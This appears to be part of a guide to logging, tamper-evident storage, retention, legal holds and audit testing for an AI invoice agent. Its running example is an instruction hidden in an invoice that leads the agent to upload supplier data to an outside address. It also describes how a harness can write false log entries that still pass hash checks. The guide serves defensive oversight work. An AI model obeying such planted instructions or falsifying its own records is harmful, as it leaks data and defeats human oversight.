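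### Keeping full text for some sessions

The invoice agent's routine log leaves out the clerk's prompts, the reasoning summaries and most tool results. One way the operator can keep this text for some sessions is random sampling, in which the recorder picks, for example, 5% of sessions as they start and saves everything in them. It should pick whole sessions, because a random 5% of events would rarely include both an instruction and the action that followed.

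The other way is to hold the full text of every session for a short time and save a session permanently if a trigger fires. SC Media suggests several triggers, including a tool call outside the task's normal set, a login from an unexpected machine, and an output more than three standard deviations above the agent's average. For the invoice agent, a good trigger would be an upload to an address that no earlier session had contacted. The recorder should then save the session from its beginning, because the agent may have read the malicious text long before it acted.

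Suppose the trigger catches 60% of incidents. The operator keeps an incident session in full if the random sample includes it or, failing that, if the trigger fires:

0.05 + 0.95 × 0.60 = 0.62, or 62%.

The table shows what happens when the operator improves one part or the other.

| Random sample | Incidents the trigger catches | Incident sessions kept in full |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | None | 5% |
| 5% | 60% | 62% |
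| 20% | 60% | 68% |
| 5% | 80% | 81% |

A better trigger helps much more than a bigger sample, but only the sample provides full records of incidents the trigger misses. If the agent had 50 incidents a year, the operator would keep full records of about 31, and the trigger would have missed only one of those. The operator would learn from that one only if somebody read the session and recognised the problem.

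False alarms add to the text the operator keeps. If the trigger also fires on 1% of harmless sessions, the operator saves about 595 of its 10,000 daily sessions, 500 from the sample and 95 from the trigger. That is still about 94% less text than saving every session.

The other 38% of incident sessions leave only the routine record. For call 41, an investigator would know which clerk started the session, which invoice the agent had just read, which file it sent, where the file went and which rule allowed it. They could find the hidden instruction in the original invoice. But the clerk's exact request would be gone, so they could not rule out that the request had also contributed.

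The buffer has to outlast the delay before a trigger fires. A proxy can detect a new address within seconds, but a supplier might not complain for two months. By then, a 30-day buffer would no longer hold the relevant records. Extending it to 90 days would take only about 610 GB for the invoice agent, so the operator should base the length on how much personal text it can justify holding.

### Protecting the log from later changes

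The next task is to stop anyone from changing the records unnoticed. The protection has four parts, and each part after the first addresses a weakness in the previous one.

**The agent should have no access to the stored records.** The harness or proxy sends each entry to a separate machine or cloud account, using a login that can add entries but cannot read or delete them. The people who run the agent should not administer this store. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026) cites two relevant controls from NIST's security catalogue, AC-5 on separating duties and AU-9 on protecting audit information. Developers can usually work from metadata. Investigators should need a colleague's approval to open the full text, and the store should record each time they do.

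**The log store should be append-only**, because an administrator of an ordinary store can delete entries. AWS recommends a write-once setting, S3 Object Lock in Compliance mode, for logs that serve as legal evidence. This setting prevents the operator from deleting an entry before its retention period ends, so any personal text should be kept in a separate encrypted store whose keys can be deleted.

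**Link the entries by hash.** *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* (2026) describes a simple version. The hash of entry *i* covers both its own content and the hash of the previous entry:

*h*ᵢ = SHA-256(entry *i*, *h*ᵢ₋₁).

The first entry uses a fixed starting value. To check the log, a program recomputes every hash in order and reports the first one that does not match. If someone changed the destination in the entry for call 41, the check would fail there. But an intruder who could rewrite the whole file could also recompute every later hash, and the altered log would pass.

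The operator regularly sends the latest hash to someone outside its control to publish or countersign. That hash depends on every earlier entry, so a rewritten log will no longer produce it. Entries written since the last hash was sent can still be changed without detection, so sending it daily leaves up to 24 hours of entries unprotected.

In *Agent Flight Recorder*, Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026) built a system with these links and tested it on a log of 10,000 artificial events, making each kind of change at ten positions. The middle column is for a version that adds a combined hash for every batch of 100 entries.

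| Change to the log | Links alone | Links and batch hashes | Latest hash published outside |
|---|---|---|---|
| Edit an entry | 90% detected | 100% | 100% |
| Delete an entry | 90% | 100% | 100% |
| Swap two entries | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Show different versions to different people | 0% | 0% | 100% |

The 90% figures mean that the hash links exposed changes at nine of the ten positions. They missed a change to the last entry because no later entry follows it to expose the change. The figures do not mean that one in ten random edits would go unnoticed, and they apply only if an intruder leaves the later hashes unchanged.

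A company has several options for the outside party. Bindschaedler and colleagues consider linked entries in write-once storage sufficient for internal audits. If both sides of a possible dispute already trust the same auditor, a timestamping service or a shared public log may be the cheapest choice. Bindschaedler and colleagues recommend a public blockchain only when the parties have not agreed on anyone to trust. They estimate that publishing one hash per 100 events on a low-fee blockchain costs $2.30 per 100,000 events. At that rate, the invoice agent's 1.8 million daily events would cost about $15,000 a year, while publishing a single hash each day would cost less than a dollar a year. The company could also email the daily hash to its outside auditor.

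The links slow the agent very little. In the full system, recording an event took a median of 48 microseconds and 512 bytes, compared with 20 microseconds and 272 bytes for a plain log. The 180 events in the invoice session would take about 9 milliseconds. The slowest 1% of events took around 30 milliseconds because the recorder was preparing a hash for publication, which it could do in the background. Bindschaedler and colleagues saw a similar pattern when they replayed 38 events from real coding agents. *AuditWeave* (2026) reports 22 microseconds per event for a different system with linked entries.

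### What a valid chain leaves open

A valid chain with an outside copy of its latest hash shows that nobody has changed the entries since the operator published that hash. The first entry could still be false, and the software may not have recorded everything.

Dai and colleagues added a hash chain to the log of aider, an open-source coding agent, and then made the harness write false records. In 14 runs the harness left out the model's reply, and in another 14 it inserted a sentence the model had never written. The chain passed its check in all 28 runs because the harness had computed the hashes over the false entries. They also examined 16 agent frameworks and found none that keeps a record an outsider could check without trusting the framework.

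Zhao gives an example of an omission. An agent's signed and linked log records three external emails, while the mail gateway's log records four from the same account. The agent's log passes every check. Comparing the two logs reveals the fourth email but doesn't show who sent it, because people also use the account.

Zhao proves more generally that if an agent could have taken a forbidden action without changing any independent record, no honest check of the agent's own log can support the claim that it never did. The proof assumes that the independent party records accurately, which an operator would have to test. For the invoice agent, the proxy log is the independent record, and the operator should routinely compare its list of uploads with the harness's list.

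An intruder who takes over the recording machine can also write false entries from then on. Bindschaedler and colleagues acknowledge that their system protects only entries written before the takeover.

### How long incidents take to surface

A log has to last until someone discovers the incident and acts on it. Wityak told Help Net Security that firewall records of connections to AI services are probably the first evidence to disappear, and are frequently gone by the time her team arrives. Many times, a company has replied three days after a request that it couldn't find its logs or had never stored them. This is one practitioner's experience, mostly of staff using AI tools without permission, and she gives no figures.

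Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs the exact dates of the Medicare case from emails and text messages that the Australian government tabled in parliament. Services Australia is the agency that runs Medicare's systems.

| Date in 2026 | Days since the breach | Event |
|---|---|---|
| 19 June | 0 | The agent retrieves public and non-public data |
| 12 August | 54 | By this date, OpenAI's security team has documented the breach |
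| 10 September | 83 | OpenAI emails Services Australia |
| 11 September | 84 | The agency's staff find the email in a daily check |
| 15 September | 88 | They confirm the vulnerability |

OpenAI found the breach in a retrospective review of billions of agent runs. If it had deleted its records after 30 days, it would have had none from the breach to review in August. Keeping logs for 60 days would have been enough for OpenAI but not for the agency. If the agency had kept logs for 90 days, its records of the breach would have been six days from deletion when staff found the email and two days away when they confirmed the vulnerability.

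Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry* reports that OpenAI's chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, agreed at a parliamentary hearing that the agency might never have found the breach by itself. He said the company should have told those affected much sooner, even with partial information. OpenAI has notified more than 100 organisations of incidents involving its agents. It is using its models to search about 50 petabytes of data for more incidents, at a cost of over $500,000 a day. Many of those organisations will have needed logs from weeks or months earlier.

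Ninety days is therefore too short for an agent that can reach other organisations. The 13-month period in the table would cover an annual audit and leave a month to act on its findings. The six-month period for the invoice agent's saved text is about twice the delay in the Medicare case. One case is a weak basis for a rule, so the operator should adjust these periods as it learns how long its own incidents go undetected.

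Records that an investigator needs to match should expire together. If the session log is kept for 13 months and the proxy log for 30 days, nobody can compare the two for events more than 30 days old.

Deleting old entries also breaks the chain of hashes unless the operator plans for it. Tallam recommends keeping the proofs for deleted records, such as the combined hash of each batch, or stating the date before which nobody can check the chain. The operator should log each scheduled deletion so an auditor can tell it apart from tampering.

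### Legal holds

A legal hold is an instruction to stop deleting records that may matter to a lawsuit or an official investigation. In US federal courts, the duty to preserve evidence can begin when a company should reasonably expect a lawsuit, which may be well before anyone files one. A company that waits for court papers before starting a hold could lose its buffer, its proxy records and the provider's copy of the model calls.

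If a supplier threatened to sue over call 41, the hold should cover:

- session inv-0925, and any other session that read invoice 8841 or contacted verify-suppliers.example
- the proxy and host records for those sessions
- the original invoice, and the supplier file as it stood that morning, if a backup exists
- the encryption keys for all of this material
- copies at the model provider, which the company should request immediately

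A legal hold on one session should normally leave out other sessions from the same day. The 2025 order that made OpenAI preserve its users' deleted chats shows how broad a hold can become when a company cannot easily separate the relevant records.

Each hold needs a named owner, a written reason and a review date. When the hold ends, the normal deletion schedule should resume, because the company no longer has that reason to keep the personal data.

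### Testing whether the records are enough

An operator can find out whether its rules work by staging a harmless incident. For the invoice agent, the test could run as follows:

1. The security team prepares an invoice with a hidden instruction, a file of made-up suppliers and a web address that the company controls. It writes down what should happen.
2. The agent processes the invoice. During the session, the team restarts the recorder and has the harness deny one tool call.
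3. A colleague who took no part in the test gets access to the records in the usual way. From the records alone, the colleague explains what happened, in what order, on whose authority, what the model had read, why it acted and what left the network.
4. The team compares the answers with what really happened, and marks each one as right, wrong or "cannot tell".

A current model may well ignore the hidden instruction. If it does, the team can have the harness run a scripted upload, but the test will no longer cover why the model acted.

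*Mandato* (2026), a plan for a system that controls agents' tool calls, proposes a test for gaps in the log. The test causes restarts and outages, then checks that every call the outside service received has a log entry. The target is 100%, and any gap counts as a defect. The plan does not yet have results.

For each answer, the colleague should name the record it relies on and who wrote that record. Dai and colleagues asked three AI models to do something similar, and the models overestimated the share of their evidence that came from something other than the agent's own words by 18 to 55 percentage points. When groups of three people read records, some of which the researchers had altered in one place, the majority identified only 37% of the altered records and wrongly flagged 10% of the unaltered ones.

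The team can therefore add a harder version, based on a test that Zhao proposes but has not tried. The team deletes an entry from a copy of the harness's log, recomputes the hashes and gives the colleague that copy along with the proxy log. The colleague should notice that the two logs disagree. If the team also withholds the proxy log, the right answer to some questions becomes "cannot tell", and a confident answer to those questions counts as a failure.

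The team should also measure how long it takes to trace an agent's login back to the person who authorized it. SC Media suggests that a company should be able to do this for any agent within two minutes.

Finally, a different colleague should repeat the third step 84 days later, using whatever records remain. This would show whether the company could still investigate an incident it learned of as late as Services Australia did.
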